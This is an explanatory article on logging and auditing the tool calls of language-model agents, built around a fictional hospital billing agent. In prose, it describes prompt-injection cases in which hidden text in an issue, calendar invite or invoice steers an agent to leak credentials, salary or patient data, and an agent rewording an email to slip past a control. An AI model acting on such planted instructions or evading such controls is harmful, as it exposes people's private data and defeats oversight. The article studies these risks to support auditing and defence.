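# Monitoring and logging the tool calls of language-model agents in regulated and high-security organisations

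## Tool calls, the logs they leave and who can read them

A language-model agent is a computer program in which a language model, the kind of system behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, chooses actions and other software carries them out. The model chooses an action by making a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function, such as one that queries a database, sends an email, makes a payment or executes a command on a server. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) defines tool calls broadly, as any request through which a model causes an outside system to read, write, compute or transmit something, so the term covers reading a record as well as changing it.

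An agent in a hospital, bank or defence body uses tool calls to reach patients' records, customers' money or restricted networks. A log of these calls is the main evidence of what the agent did and one of the main places where a breach can show up. It is also a second store of the same confidential material. Many organisations will soon have to manage such logs, and few seem ready. *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (Wang, Sun and colleagues, 2026) cites a Deloitte survey in which 74% of companies expected to make at least moderate use of agents within two years, while 21% reported a mature way of governing them.

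### How a tool call works

The model runs nothing itself. It produces text, and a program around it, the agent harness, turns some of that text into action. One pass through the loop goes like this:

1. The harness collects descriptions of the available tools. Each description gives a name, an explanation in ordinary language and a schema, which lists the arguments (the values the tool expects) and their types.
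2. The harness sends these descriptions to the model, together with the user's request.
3. The model generates its output. If it selects a tool, the output contains the tool's name and a set of arguments in a fixed format.
4. The harness parses the output, may check it against a list of permissions or ask a person to approve it, and then runs the function or forwards the call to the server that hosts it.
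5. The tool returns a result. The harness adds the result to the conversation and calls the model again, and the loop continues until the model answers without asking for a tool.

Many agents find and call their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for tools that run on separate servers. The project behind it, Model Context Protocol (2026), counted close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits in July 2026. The specification page, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), gives the example of a call to a weather service. The request contains the name `get_weather` and the argument "New York", and the response contains a line of text with the temperature. Failed calls also return text. When a tool rejects a date or cannot reach a database, the specification recommends that the harness pass the error message to the model, so that the model can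 correct its arguments and try again. Error messages are therefore part of the result, and they are sent and stored wherever other results are.

The harness usually sends the whole conversation to the model again at every turn, including earlier tool results. An organisation that stops recording tool results but still records model inputs therefore still has the results. For example, the sample model input in OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, part of an open standard for the format of such records, contains a complete tool call and its result in the middle of the chat history.

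### A billing agent and its three calls

An imaginary hospital with 200,000 patients will serve as the example from here on. An insurer has queried an invoice, and a clerk in the billing office asks the hospital's agent to answer. The agent makes three calls, and a log with everything switched on might hold these entries:

```
09:14:02  lookup_patient
  arguments  name: "Maria Keller", born: "1961-03-08"
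  result     patient: "P-118204", insurer: "Northfield Mutual",
             balance_due: 1840.00

09:14:05  query_oncology_registry
  arguments  patient: "P-118204", since: "2026-09-01"
  result     diagnosis: "C50.9", treatment: "chemotherapy, 4 sessions"

09:14:11  send_email
  arguments  to: "claims@northfield.example", subject: "Invoice 60713",
             body: "Mrs Keller received four sessions of chemotherapy..."
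  result     status: "accepted"
```

The tool name `lookup_patient` reveals almost nothing, since hospitals look up patients all day. But the call's arguments identify a woman by name and date of birth, and the result adds her insurer and what she owes.

Anyone who can link a `query_oncology_registry` call to patient P-118204 can guess from the tool's name alone that the hospital is treating her for cancer. The arguments contain her patient number, which provides that link, and the result contains C50.9, the international code for breast cancer with no more specific site given.

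Most of what `send_email` discloses is in its arguments. The tool's name shows that a message was sent, and the result shows only that the mail server accepted it. The email's body repeats the treatment in plain words, so deleting the registry's result from the log would achieve little while the body remains there.

If the hospital records model inputs as well as tool results, the registry's answer appears in the logs three times: as the result of its own call, in the input from which the model produced the email, and in the input for the final reply to the clerk. Mrs Keller's name and balance appear even more often.

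### Who holds a copy

Engineers call the ordered record of one agent run a trace, and each step in it a span. *When Agentic Executions Fail* (2026) reports that a typical run has tens to a few hundred spans, and that one run of a database assistant had 64. Each span has an identifier, a type, a start time, a duration and a status, and may also include the step's input and output text. Recording this text is called content capture, and operators can usually turn it on or off.

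Several other systems may sit between the agent and its tools, or collect records from them. A gateway is a server that all of an organisation's tool calls pass through, so that it can check and record them in one place. An observability vendor is an outside company that stores and displays a customer's traces. According to *Reasoning Provenance for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026), LangSmith, Langfuse and Datadog all capture tool calls together with the model's inputs and outputs. A security team uses a security information and event management (SIEM) system to gather logs from across the organisation and run detection rules on them. Data-loss prevention (DLP) controls look for sensitive data leaving the organisation, such as a patient number in an email, and block or report it.

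A single call to `query_oncology_registry` can leave traces with six parties:

| Holder | What reaches it |
|---|---|
| Model provider | The name and arguments, which its model generated, and the result once the harness sends it back |
| Agent harness | The whole call, the clerk's request and the conversation around them |
| Gateway | The tool's name, and the arguments and result if it reads message contents |
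| Tool server | The arguments and the result, often without the clerk's original request |
| Observability vendor | The name, time and status, plus arguments and result where content capture is on |
| SIEM | Whichever fields and alerts the security team forwards to it |

Other equipment may also see part of the call. Since July 2026, MCP has required the tool's name to be sent in a web header so that gateways can route and authorise calls without opening the message. A server's developer can mark individual arguments to be sent the same way. Model Context Protocol warns developers against marking passwords, keys or personal data, because network intermediaries can read the headers. The tool's name must still be in the header, even if it is sensitive. A proxy that records headers could therefore store `query_oncology_registry` in a log that nobody at the hospital thinks of as medical.

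The hospital has least control over the copies held by outside companies. By default, OpenAI keeps logs for detecting abuse for up to 30 days. These may contain prompts and responses, which for an agent include tool results and arguments. OpenAI's Conversations API stores dialogue on OpenAI's servers until the customer deletes it. Data that an agent sends to another company's MCP server is subject to that company's retention policy. Anthropic's *How long do you store my organization’s data?* states that Anthropic deletes API users' data within 30 days by default, except when it needs the data to meet legal duties or enforce its usage policy.

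Both companies also offer zero data retention, under which the provider keeps no prompts or responses after processing a request. In 2026 this option became less dependable for the most capable models. Axios' *OpenAI previews zero-retention safety system as Anthropic requires data logs* (2026) reports that Anthropic announced it would require 30 days' retention on its most capable models for security reasons, a change aimed at customers who until then had zero retention. OpenAI agreed that some dangers show only across several interactions, such as when a user asks about a weakness in a company's software in one conversation and about remote access in another. OpenAI's *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models* (2026) previewed its response in August, automated monitoring that the company describes as compatible with zero retention. However, OpenAI reserves the right in its documentation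 to withdraw zero retention from particular customers on particular models, with notice.

Anthropic has since partly reversed this policy. It is introducing, in phases from autumn 2026, an option for customers to keep the monitoring data in cloud storage they control. In the meantime, it offers eligible customers zero retention on its Fable models for internal business use. At the hospital, a change of model can create a 30-day copy of Mrs Keller's diagnosis where there was none, even if nobody changes the hospital's own logging settings.

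### Three reasons to keep a log

*Externalization in LLM Agents* (2026) lists debugging, compliance auditing and post-incident analysis as uses of the same structured log. One log can serve all three, but developers, security staff and lawyers want different information from it, kept for different lengths of time.

Developers who debug an agent want a lot of content. Wang, Pei and colleagues (2026) point out in *Agent System Operations* that an agent can finish a task with no error and still have done it wrongly. A list of successful statuses may therefore hide the fault. To find out why the billing agent quoted the wrong treatment dates, a developer has to read what the registry returned and what the model then wrote. Developers rarely need this content after the repair, which may take days or weeks. A sample of runs is often enough, and some of the work needs no content at all. *PegasusAI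 Studio* (2026) describes an agent platform for scientific computing that always collects usage figures, such as the duration of tool calls, but keeps prompts and tool arguments only for users who have opted in.

A security team looking for breaches needs a record of every call, because a sample may miss the one run that matters. It needs the records promptly and in a uniform format, so that detection rules can compare agents with each other and with the rest of the network. The team needs to know who ran the agent, how many records a query returned and where an email went, but often doesn't need the text of the email. It also wants months of history, because an intrusion may stay hidden for a long time.

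Legal evidence requires an audit trail, which is a log that the organisation protects from alteration and ties to identified users and agents. *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* (2026) describes one as a tamper-evident ledger, meaning that later changes to it can be detected. Laws and contracts set the retention period, which can run to years. The trail also needs to record who authorised an action and under which rule, because a court or regulator will ask. In *When Agents Act Unwatched*, Shi and DiFranzo (2026) argue that records built for debugging tend not to capture this adequately. They note that a tool history may show that a message was sent, but not which request authorised the recipient, which policy allowed the message or whether it contained private data.

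The limited survey evidence is consistent with this. Surapani and colleagues cite a 2026 poll by the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, and the company Strata, in which only 28% of organisations could trace agents' actions to a responsible person in all their environments, but they qualify the result with "if representative". Shi and DiFranzo examined 63 public papers and documents about agents and found that 37 clearly described monitoring or traces, but only 9 clearly described privacy and surveillance concerns. They picked documents rich in technical detail, so the counts reflect what builders choose to write about and can't show how many deployed systems neglect privacy.

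A hospital could keep a separate store for each purpose, with its own contents and deletion date. Keeping everything in one store for the longest of the three periods is simpler, but text a developer needed for a week then stays available for years.

### The investigator and the thief

Suppose that the address in `send_email` had belonged to a stranger instead of the insurer. The recipient's address in the log would expose this. The hospital would need the body of the message to tell Mrs Keller what leaked, and patient numbers from every run the agent has made to find other victims among its 200,000 patients. Someone who steals the log gets the same fields, with names, birth dates, debts and diagnoses already matched to one another. The hospital otherwise keeps these in separate systems with separate access rules. Tool names and error messages also show roughly how those systems are organised.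 Surapani and colleagues call a complete log a "high-value target" for this reason.

MCP's page on tools advises clients to log tool usage for audit purposes. But Model Context Protocol's *Logging* (2026) forbids credentials, personal information and internal details that could help an attacker in the messages that tool servers send to clients about their own operation. The page's sample message reports a failed database connection and includes the database's host and port. These are placeholder values, but a real server that followed the example would disclose real ones. MCP has since deprecated this logging feature and points developers of remote servers to OpenTelemetry.

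OpenTelemetry's conventions, which are still under development, recommend recording a tool's name but leave out its arguments and result unless the operator opts in, and they warn that both may be sensitive. A hospital that keeps those defaults has far less sensitive data in its logs that could be stolen. But if an insurer reports that an email from the hospital's agent never arrived, the log will show that the agent queried the oncology registry and sent a message six seconds later, but not which patient the query concerned or who received the message.

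## What to record about each tool call

The hospital can add the patient and the email's recipient to its log by turning on arguments and results. The log would still leave out the clerk, the version of each tool and whether anyone approved the message. A fuller entry for the `send_email` call might look like this:

```
call         c-3, in run r-5521
time         09:14:11
user         clerk-204
agent        billing-agent, version 4.2
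chain        clerk-204 > billing-agent > send_email
task         "Answer Northfield's query about invoice 60713"
tool         send_email, version 2.1, schema 7be1...
arguments    to: "claims@northfield.example", subject: ..., body: ...
result       status: "accepted"
data class   patient data
decision     allowed, rule "billing agent may send email"
approval     none
attempt      1
inputs from  c-1, c-2
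```

Two published lists cover most of these fields. Surapani and colleagues ask for the task, the permissions in force, the arguments (with sensitive values removed), the result, the chain of delegation at the time of the call, the policy decision and links to whatever led to the call. *Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) describes each step of a run by its type, input, output, time and context, which includes the state of any approval, the chain of callers and the phase of the run. It gives less weight to the task but stresses retries and failed attempts, which the first list doesn't mention.

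### The person, the agent and the task

The user field records who wanted the call made. This information is easily lost because an agent usually connects to a database or mail server under its own account. Surapani and colleagues examined how two common arrangements handle this. On Amazon Bedrock Agents, a managed cloud platform, an investigator can attribute every call to a verified platform identity, but that identity contains nothing about the person who set the task. Under MCP's authorisation scheme, the client and server authenticate, but the access token does not identify that person. In both cases, the harness has to add the user's name, because that is where the user logged in.

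Surapani and colleagues call this the attribution gap. They argue that an authenticated call that nobody can trace to a person is more dangerous than an unauthenticated one, because it passes every formal check and looks legitimate.

The agent field needs a version as well as a name. The hospital may change the agent's instructions or underlying model and nothing else. If the agent starts quoting diagnoses in emails, an investigator will want to know whether it started before or after the change.

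When agents hand work to each other, the harness has to record the full delegation chain at the time of the call, since permissions may have changed by the time anyone reviews it. Nian and colleagues describe an agent that delegates a task to a second agent, which uses another company's add-on, which calls an outside service and gets sensitive data back. If the log holds only the second agent's call, an auditor can see who made the request but not who started the work or how the add-on became involved. The delegation chain seems to be one of the harder fields to fill. Aegis, a tool by some of the same researchers that checks calls before they run, records the immediate caller and the session but not the full chain.

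The task field records what the call was supposed to achieve. Without it, a hijacked agent's calls can look like normal work. *Clawed and Dangerous* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a developer who asks an agent to summarise recent issues in a software project and update the documentation. One issue contains hidden instructions to read a file of cloud credentials, send its contents to an outside address and delete the project's history. The agent has the developer's permissions, so each step is an ordinary action, and the logs contain "only a sequence of seemingly legitimate tool invocations". If each entry also recorded the task, a reviewer could ask why summarising issues required reading a credentials file.

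But the task cannot establish what the person intended. Surapani and colleagues point out that a digital signature can prove that the holder of a key delegated authority, but not that a human understood and wanted the particular action that followed. The clerk asked for an answer about an invoice, and only the clerk can say whether that included telling the insurer about four sessions of chemotherapy. The log can only show how the request was worded. That wording may contain patient data too, if the clerk typed Mrs Keller's name.

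### The tool and the data

A tool's name identifies the function that the agent asked for, but that function can change while the name stays the same. Surapani and colleagues list several ways in which a tool's description can mislead: an attacker writes it to encourage misuse, it leaves out important limits or side effects, or the code changes and the description does not. They recommend tying each tool to an identity, a version, the registry it came from and a hash of its schema. A hash is a short fingerprint computed from a text, and it changes if the text is edited. If `query_oncology_registry` began to return whole treatment histories after an update, a reviewer could use the version field to explain why the agent's results grew that month. The schema hash alone might not reveal the update, because a developer can change what a tool returns without changing the arguments it accepts.

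The arguments show what the agent asked for and where it sent data, but some matter far more than others to an investigator. In `send_email`, the `to` address shows whether data left the hospital, while the subject line rarely adds much. In a database query, the patient number and date range show how much the agent tried to read.

The result records what the agent received, which may be more than it asked for. For calls that change something, the result is also evidence that the change took place, but this evidence is often partial. For example, a mail server's "accepted" reply does not confirm that the message was delivered.

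The data class is a label such as "public" or "patient data". It lets the hospital check rules about sensitive data without storing the data. The registry's server can attach the label to everything it returns, but the label then has to follow the data into later calls, which is difficult when a model rewrites what it has read. For example, the email to the insurer paraphrases the registry's answer. Surapani and colleagues list tracking through summaries as an open problem. As a precaution, the harness could label every call in a run as patient data once the agent has read any. This would over-label harmless calls, but it wouldn't depend on recognising a diagnosis in a rewritten sentence.

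### Decisions, approvals and failed attempts

Many organisations use a control that can allow a tool call, block it or hold it for a person to review. The decision field records what this control did and which rule it applied. Surapani and colleagues describe a case in which a user asks a calendar assistant to summarise the week's meetings, and one invitation contains an instruction to send the user's salary information to an outside address. The assistant proposes two calls, one to read the salary and one to send an email. The control blocks both because the task covered only reading the calendar and because the arguments came from an untrusted source. It then logs the chain of callers, the arguments with sensitive values removed, the rule that matched, the untrusted sources and the outcome.

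Neither tool ran, so if a log creates entries only when tools execute, its only record of the attack would be a successful call to read a calendar.

The approval field should record the approver's name, the time and exactly what the approver saw. Nian and colleagues show why with an example in which an agent queries customer records and then sends an email. The log contains both calls, but it omits that the agent first tried to send a different email, that a policy check blocked it, that the agent changed the text, and that a person approved the second version. An auditor who sees only the query and the final email can't tell whether the agent complied from the start or reworded the email to get past a control.

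An approval also means little if the approver saw only the question "allow this action?". Surapani and colleagues want the approver to see the arguments, the class of data and the sources that influenced the request. They warn that too many prompts lead people to approve mechanically. The time field helps detect this, because an approval given one second after a long email appeared on screen is unlikely to reflect a careful reading.

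Each retry and failure needs its own log entry, with an attempt number that links it to the other attempts at the same call. If the mail server times out and the harness resends an email to an insurer, the insurer may receive two copies, but a log of successes alone would show one. Repeated failures can also be a warning sign, such as when an agent looks up forty nonexistent patient numbers in a row.

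Timestamps put the calls in order, but clocks on different machines disagree, and several agents may work at once. The link to earlier steps is more reliable where it exists. It shows what the call relied on, which Nian and colleagues say auditors usually have to infer from ordinary traces. Surapani and colleagues consider these links the field that takes the most resources to record and search at scale, and mention the option of keeping them in full for high-risk actions and in summary for the rest. The harness can record that the results of c-1 and c-2 were in the model's input when it wrote the email, but it can't record which of them the model used.

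### Measuring whether the record is good enough

Nian and colleagues start from what an auditor has to deliver: an action, its context, a verdict on whether it complied with a policy, the party responsible, and a guarantee that nobody has altered the evidence. Each part requires a different property of the record. They call these properties the five dimensions of auditability and give two metrics for each.

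| Dimension | Auditor's question | Metrics |
|---|---|---|
| Action recoverability | What happened? | Action coverage rate: share of relevant actions that appear in the record at all. Record fidelity: average share of the needed fields present for those actions |
| Lifecycle coverage | In what context? | Lifecycle phase coverage: share of the run's phases that the record shows. Gap burden: total length of the missing phases, in steps or in time |
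| Policy checkability | Did it comply? | Structural policy decidability rate: share of rules that the record can settle. Audit detection latency: time from a violation until the record can reveal it |
| Responsibility attribution | Who was responsible? | Attribution completeness: share of actions traceable all the way to their origin. Attribution chain depth: average number of links recovered |
| Evidence integrity | Can anyone trust the evidence? | Integrity strength: a scale from 0 to 3. Verification cost: time needed to check the whole record |

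The billing run shows why each dimension needs more than one number. With default OpenTelemetry settings, all three calls appear in the log, so action coverage is 3/3. Suppose the hospital decides it needs four fields to reconstruct a call: tool name, time, arguments and result. The default settings record only two of these for each call, so record fidelity is 0.5.

Suppose a control had blocked the agent's first email and the clerk had approved a second version. The run would then have five phases: reading records, the blocked attempt, rewriting, approval and sending. A log that records only the reading and the sending has a phase coverage of 2/5, or 0.4, and a gap burden of three steps if each missing phase took one step. If the rewriting had taken a thousand steps, coverage would still be 0.4, but the gap burden would be 1,002 steps. Nian and colleagues acknowledge that the coverage metric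 does not distinguish a phase that never happened from one that nobody recorded. They suggest that explicit markers at the start and end of each phase may be needed.

Each call in the example has a true attribution chain of three links: the tool, the agent and the clerk. If the log records the agent's service account but no user, an auditor can recover only the tool and the agent for each call. The average depth is then 2, but completeness is zero because no call can be traced to a person.

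At level 0 of the integrity scale, someone could change an entry without detection. At level 1, the log is append-only, so nobody can delete or reorder entries. Level 2 adds a hash chain, in which each entry contains a fingerprint of the one before, and level 3 adds digital signatures that outsiders can check. The other four dimensions depend on this one, since a complete record is of little use if the agent's operator could have rewritten it.

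A run counts as auditable if it meets a chosen threshold on seven of the ten metrics. The other three (detection latency, chain depth and verification cost) describe how well or how quickly an audit would go. The paper gives no guidance on where to set the thresholds. Its researchers have not yet done a complete audit of a deployed system using all five dimensions. They derive the list from the parts of a verdict but do not formally prove that it is complete.

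A larger gap for a hospital is that the dimensions leave out privacy, which Nian and colleagues treat as a constraint on the record's design. A log that copied every patient's file in full would lose no points on any of the ten metrics, except perhaps for the time needed to verify it. A hospital can therefore use the scores to find out that it records too little, but not that it records too much.

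### When a rule can be judged neither kept nor broken

The policy metrics apply to structural rules, which a computer can check from the fields of a log. Take this one: no email to an outside address after reading patient data without approval. Checking it against a run takes five pieces of information: the tool's name, the order of the calls, the class of data in the earlier results, the recipient and the approval. With the full entries for run r-5521, the check goes as follows:

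1. Calls c-1 and c-2 returned patient data.
2. Call c-3 came later and sent an email.
3. The recipient, `claims@northfield.example`, is outside the hospital.
4. The approval field contains "none".

The agent broke the rule. If the field had contained a valid approval by the clerk, the agent would have kept it.

If the log omits the recipient, it shows that the agent read patient data and then emailed someone without approval, but not whether the agent broke the rule. An email to the insurer would break it and an email to a colleague in the next office would not, yet both would leave identical entries. Recording the subject line, the duration and the mail server's response in more detail would not help, and neither would more entries of the same kind.

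Nian and colleagues state this in general form as their Proposition 1. Let *F* be the set of fields that a rule requires, and *S* the non-empty set of steps in a run that could help decide it. If some field in *F* is missing from everything recorded about every step in *S*, the rule's outcome is ⊥, their symbol for undecidable. This follows because a verdict requires every field in *F* to appear somewhere in the pooled evidence about those steps. They call it "not a deep result", but it means that whoever chooses the log's fields also decides which rules anyone can check later, since analysis after the event can't restore a field that left no trace.

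The hospital's first log, which records all arguments and results, fails in this way. It contains Mrs Keller's diagnosis and the full text of the email but has no approval field, so nobody can tell from the log whether that run, or any similar one, followed the rule.

Pooling matters because separate records of the same step can fill gaps in each other. If the agent's log lacks the recipient but the mail server's log has it, and a shared identifier links the two entries, the hospital can still reach a verdict. If the mail log arrives only overnight, the 09:14 email has a detection latency of many hours.

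The proposition can treat an outcome as undecidable even when the log contains enough to settle it. If the log shows that the clerk approved the email, the agent kept the rule whoever received it, and a checker that tests the conditions one by one could conclude this without the address. The outcome is still undecidable under the formal definition because the recipient is a required field. Even having every required field somewhere in the run doesn't guarantee a verdict. An agent may send two emails, and the recipient of one can't be inferred from the recipient of the other.

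The required field can contain less information than the original value. This rule depends only on whether the address is outside the hospital, so recording "outside" would be enough to check it. A rule that allowed email only to insurers under contract would require more information about the recipient.

Some important rules can't be checked from fields alone. Compliance with "The email must not reveal more than the insurer needs" depends on the meaning of the text, so somebody has to read the body and judge. Nian and colleagues leave rules of this kind as an open problem.

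### What the OpenTelemetry conventions cover

Most developers will not design a log format from scratch. OpenTelemetry's conventions for generative AI give common names to the fields, so that a tool from one company can read traces produced by another. The central record for a tool call is the `execute_tool` span. The published text sorts its fields, which it calls attributes, by how strongly it asks for them:

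| Level | Attributes of the `execute_tool` span |
|---|---|
| Required | The name of the operation; the class of error, if the call failed |
| Recommended | The tool's name; also its description, its type and an identifier for the call, where available |
| Opt-in | The arguments; the result |

Greptime (2026), a database company, reports that version 1.41 of the conventions requires the span name to include the tool's name. A hospital that follows this version will have spans with names like `execute_tool query_oncology_registry`, so removing the separate tool-name attribute would still leave the tool's name in the span name.

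The convention defines the result attribute for successful calls. When a call fails, the span must instead give a class of error, such as "timeout" or the code 500. This keeps error messages out of the result attribute, but they still reach the log if the hospital records model inputs.

OpenTelemetry's reasons for caution about recording content concern model instructions, inputs and outputs, which repeat the arguments and results of tool calls. They are often large and sensitive, so recording them can be expensive, conflict with regulation, and expose users' data to people who need only operational facts. Developers who still want the content can record it on the spans, or put it in a separate store and leave only a reference on the span. OpenTelemetry considers the first option suitable where volumes are manageable and either privacy rules don't apply or the storage complies with them,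 for example in testing before release. It recommends the second for production systems with large volumes or sensitive data. A separate store can have its own access rules, so an engineer could see that a call took nine seconds without being able to read the diagnosis it contained.

For the second option, OpenTelemetry says that if software supports an upload routine for such content, the routine should work independently of the opt-in settings and run even for traces that sampling would otherwise discard. An administrator who finds content capture switched off therefore also needs to check for an upload routine.

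The conventions leave several fields in the full `send_email` entry to the operator. OpenTelemetry's *Gen AI* registry page lists attributes for the agent's identifier and version, the conversation and the call. It has no dedicated attributes for the human user, the delegation chain, the data class, the policy decision, the approval or the tool's version. A hospital could follow the conventions exactly, with every opt-in field switched on, and still be unable to check the rule about outside emails. Operators who need an audit trail will have to add their own attributes.

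The names may also change. OpenTelemetry's *Moved* says that the conventions now have their own repository and that nobody maintains the old page. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, dates the move to June 2026 and reports that on 21 August the new repository still had the status "Development" and no official release. Wang, who writes for a company that sells an AI gateway, recommends that organisations treat the attributes they emit as a versioned interface and test it against the systems that read it. This matters more for audit than for debugging. If an update renames an attribute, a detection rule that searches for the old name will find nothing and may raise no error.

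The Agent Audit Trail, a proposed format designed more for auditing, is a draft submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards. It is an individual submission with no official standing, so a supplier who advertises compliance with it is not offering compliance with an IETF standard.

### The model's written reasoning

Many models write out some reasoning before they choose a tool, and a harness that receives this text can log it, which can save an investigator hours. Suppose the billing agent had sent Mrs Keller's treatment details to a stranger, and its reasoning included "the note on the invoice asks me to copy this address". The investigator would know at once to examine the invoice. Reasoning can also show that the agent misread a date or assumed it had a permission that it lacked, neither of which is obvious from a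 list of calls.

The reasoning text is sensitive, however. A model that reasons about a diagnosis repeats the diagnosis, often with guesses that aren't in the patient's file. Surapani and colleagues include intermediate reasoning among the contents that make a complete log attractive to attackers. The reasoning text may also be unavailable. OpenTelemetry has an attribute for the number of reasoning tokens (the pieces of text that a model generates while reasoning), but this count doesn't reveal what the text contains. Wang notes that the agent spans do not expose a model's private reasoning, and some providers return only a summary of it.

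Reasoning is also weak evidence of why the agent acted. The model generates it like any other text and can leave out whatever influenced the next call. Researchers at Anthropic tested this in *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think* (2025) by adding hints about the answer to test questions. When a hint changed the model's answer, Claude 3.7 Sonnet mentioned the hint in its reasoning 25% of the time, and DeepSeek's R1 did so 39% of the time. Both models are now old and the tasks were exam questions, so the percentages may not apply to today's agents. But an instruction hidden in an invoice is a similar kind of influence, and reasoning that doesn't mention it would not rule out the invoice as the cause of a call.

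The other fields are more reliable than the agent's reasoning. In the calendar assistant example, the control used the scope of the task and the source of the arguments to refuse both calls, without consulting any reasoning. An investigator who suspects the invoice can also rerun the agent in a test environment, with and without the suspicious note, and compare the calls it makes. This requires a record of what the model originally received, and it takes several attempts because a model's output varies from run to run. Surapani and colleagues describe PCAS, a research system that captures the dependencies between steps as they execute and supports re-running selected parts. If the outside address appears only in runs that include the note, that is much better evidence of the cause than the agent's own explanation.

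## Where tool calls are captured and how the record is protected from alteration

The program that writes a log can record only what passes through it, so the log may contain every field on the hospital's list and still miss part of what an agent did. Whoever controls the log may also be able to change it later.

### A shell command that contacts a second service

Suppose the hospital gives its billing agent another tool, `run_shell`, which executes commands on a server. A clerk asks for October's invoices as PDF files, and the agent runs a conversion script that a contractor wrote. The harness logs one call:

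```
09:40:17  run_shell
  arguments  command: "./convert_invoices.sh 2026-10"
  result     exit code: 0, output: "212 invoices converted"
```

This looks complete, with one entry for one tool call, full arguments, a result and no error. But the script doesn't convert anything itself. It uploads the invoices to a conversion service on the internet and downloads the PDFs. A sensor in the server's operating system could record that:

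```
09:40:17  start    convert_invoices.sh   parent: billing-agent
09:40:18  read     212 files in /billing/2026-10
09:40:18  start    curl                  parent: convert_invoices.sh
09:40:19  connect  pdf-tools.example     sent: 8.1 MB
```

`curl` is a common program for transferring data over the web. The sensor's record shows that 212 invoices probably left the hospital, but not who asked for them or why. Nian and colleagues count external requests among the actions an audit needs, so if the call and the upload are the two relevant actions here, the harness log has an action coverage of 1/2. Someone with only the harness log would calculate 1/1.

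| Capture point | What it records here | What it misses | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code library in the application | The call, its arguments and result | The upload, and any tool that a developer forgot to connect to the library | The application's developers |
| Agent harness | The same, plus the clerk's request and the model's input | The upload | The hospital's developers or the agent's supplier |
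| Gateway | Nothing, because the shell runs locally and the call never passes through it | The whole event | The hospital's platform or security team |
| Tool server (here, the conversion service) | The upload and the invoices in it | The clerk, the agent and the task | An outside company |
| Operating system | The programs, files and connection | The clerk's request and the encrypted contents | The hospital's IT staff |

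Nian and colleagues found a real example of this pattern when they scanned OpenClaw, an open-source AI assistant. One community-made add-on contained a command that downloads a script from the web and runs it immediately. The script runs outside any protected record, and an investigator can't trace its actions back through the add-on.

A gateway can supply the shared identifier needed to combine records from several capture points. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a design for securing agents on large clusters of servers, puts a gateway between agents and their tool servers. The gateway submits the agent, user, tool and arguments to a policy check, then logs the call with the decision and a trace identifier that also appears in other logs. This works for calls that go through the gateway, but a script's `curl` upload would not carry the identifier unless the script's author had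 arranged it. The hospital would then have to match the upload to the clerk's request by time and parent program.

In *One Policy, Four Interception Points*, Shaw (2026) measured how much the choice of capture point matters in Oathpost, a system Shaw built to check and record tool calls. Its four capture points are a code library, an MCP gateway, a network proxy, and a hook, which is a small program that a coding agent runs before each call. The library can read every argument but not the network destination, while the proxy can read the destination but not the tool's definition. Of 1,540 test cases that the central policy service could judge, 367 needed something the proxy could not supply, 1,188 something the hook could not, and 1,195 something the gateway could not. Most of the shortfall at the hook and gateway came from how the test software was set up, so these figures don't measure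 gateways in general.

Where a capture point could handle a case, its decisions and records matched the library's in all 1,865 comparisons. The one exception was a defect in the hook that made it skip the policy service when it received an unusual argument value, so no decision was recorded. In sessions configured to continue after such failures, the hook also did not stop the call.

### What only the harness sees

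The harness also decides what the model reads. For example, it shortens long conversations and saves notes that later runs can load. If a clerk writes "do not mention diagnoses to insurers" and the harness drops that line when it summarises the conversation, the agent may email a diagnosis to an insurer. A log of tool calls would include the email but not show that the instruction had been dropped.

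Shah and Kathrotia (2026), in *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, propose that the harness record eight kinds of transfer like these, of which tool calls are one. They compared several logs on 240 controlled runs, half of them with a deliberate fault from one of six families:

| Log | Faulty runs detected | Healthy runs wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Tool calls only | 16.7% | 0% |
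| OpenTelemetry-style spans | 23.3% | 35.0% |
| All eight transfers, simple checks only | 91.7% | 0% |
| All eight transfers, with checks by a model | 98.3% | 0% |

The simple checks missed cases where a summary dropped an instruction with no identifier to search for. Recording added little overhead, with a median of 12 to 82 microseconds per transfer and an average of 524 bytes per record.

The researchers built the faults around the transfers that their own format records, which favours that format. The tool-call log caught 20 faulty runs, the same number as in one of the six families. The experiment shows that a tool-call log can miss whole classes of fault, but not how common those faults are in practice. The design also depends on attackers being unable to modify the harness or its log store. Shah and Kathrotia acknowledge that an attacker could still steer an agent onto a channel that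 the harness doesn't log. An upload from inside a script is one such channel.

### Agent products missing from customers' audit logs

Organisations that buy a finished agent depend on its supplier for much of the record. Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, is one example. In March 2026, according to Anthropic's *Use Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans*, Cowork activity did not appear in audit logs, data exports or the Compliance API, through which customers retrieve records of their staff's use of Claude. Anthropic told organisations that needed audit trails for compliance not to enable Cowork for regulated work.

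Anthropic has since closed most of this gap for customers on its Enterprise plan. Hyrax's *Anthropic's Compliance API Logs Claude Code Sessions, Half a Story* (2026) dates the new interface for sessions on users' own machines to 11 August. Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* announced a beta version covering Cowork and Claude Code, its coding agent. Anthropic's *Retrieve session transcripts* lists what the interface still leaves out:

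- Claude Code sessions that run in the cloud, use a developer's API key, or reach the model through Amazon, Google or Microsoft
- sessions on users' machines under zero data retention
- for organisations with settings for HIPAA (the US health-privacy law) switched on, sessions on users' machines in any product except Cowork and Claude Code

The HIPAA settings also shorten the storage period for these sessions from a default of six years to 30 days, so a hospital that needs a longer audit trail has to export them within that period. By default, the interface truncates each tool input, and each piece of text in a result, to 10,000 bytes. Reviewers can request up to about a megabyte, which they may need if the patient they are looking for appears at the end of a long query result.

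Anthropic's *Compliance API* limits session transcripts to Enterprise customers. Customers on the smaller Team plan can stream Cowork's events through OpenTelemetry, but Anthropic warns that this does not replace audit logging for compliance. The stream is also easy to misconfigure. According to Anthropic's *Monitor Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry*, Cowork sends no events until an administrator enters an address for them. Anthropic's *Monitoring usage* adds that this setting covers Cowork only, so Claude Code sends nothing to that address. A security team that sees events from Cowork could therefore wrongly conclude that its programmers aren't using agents.

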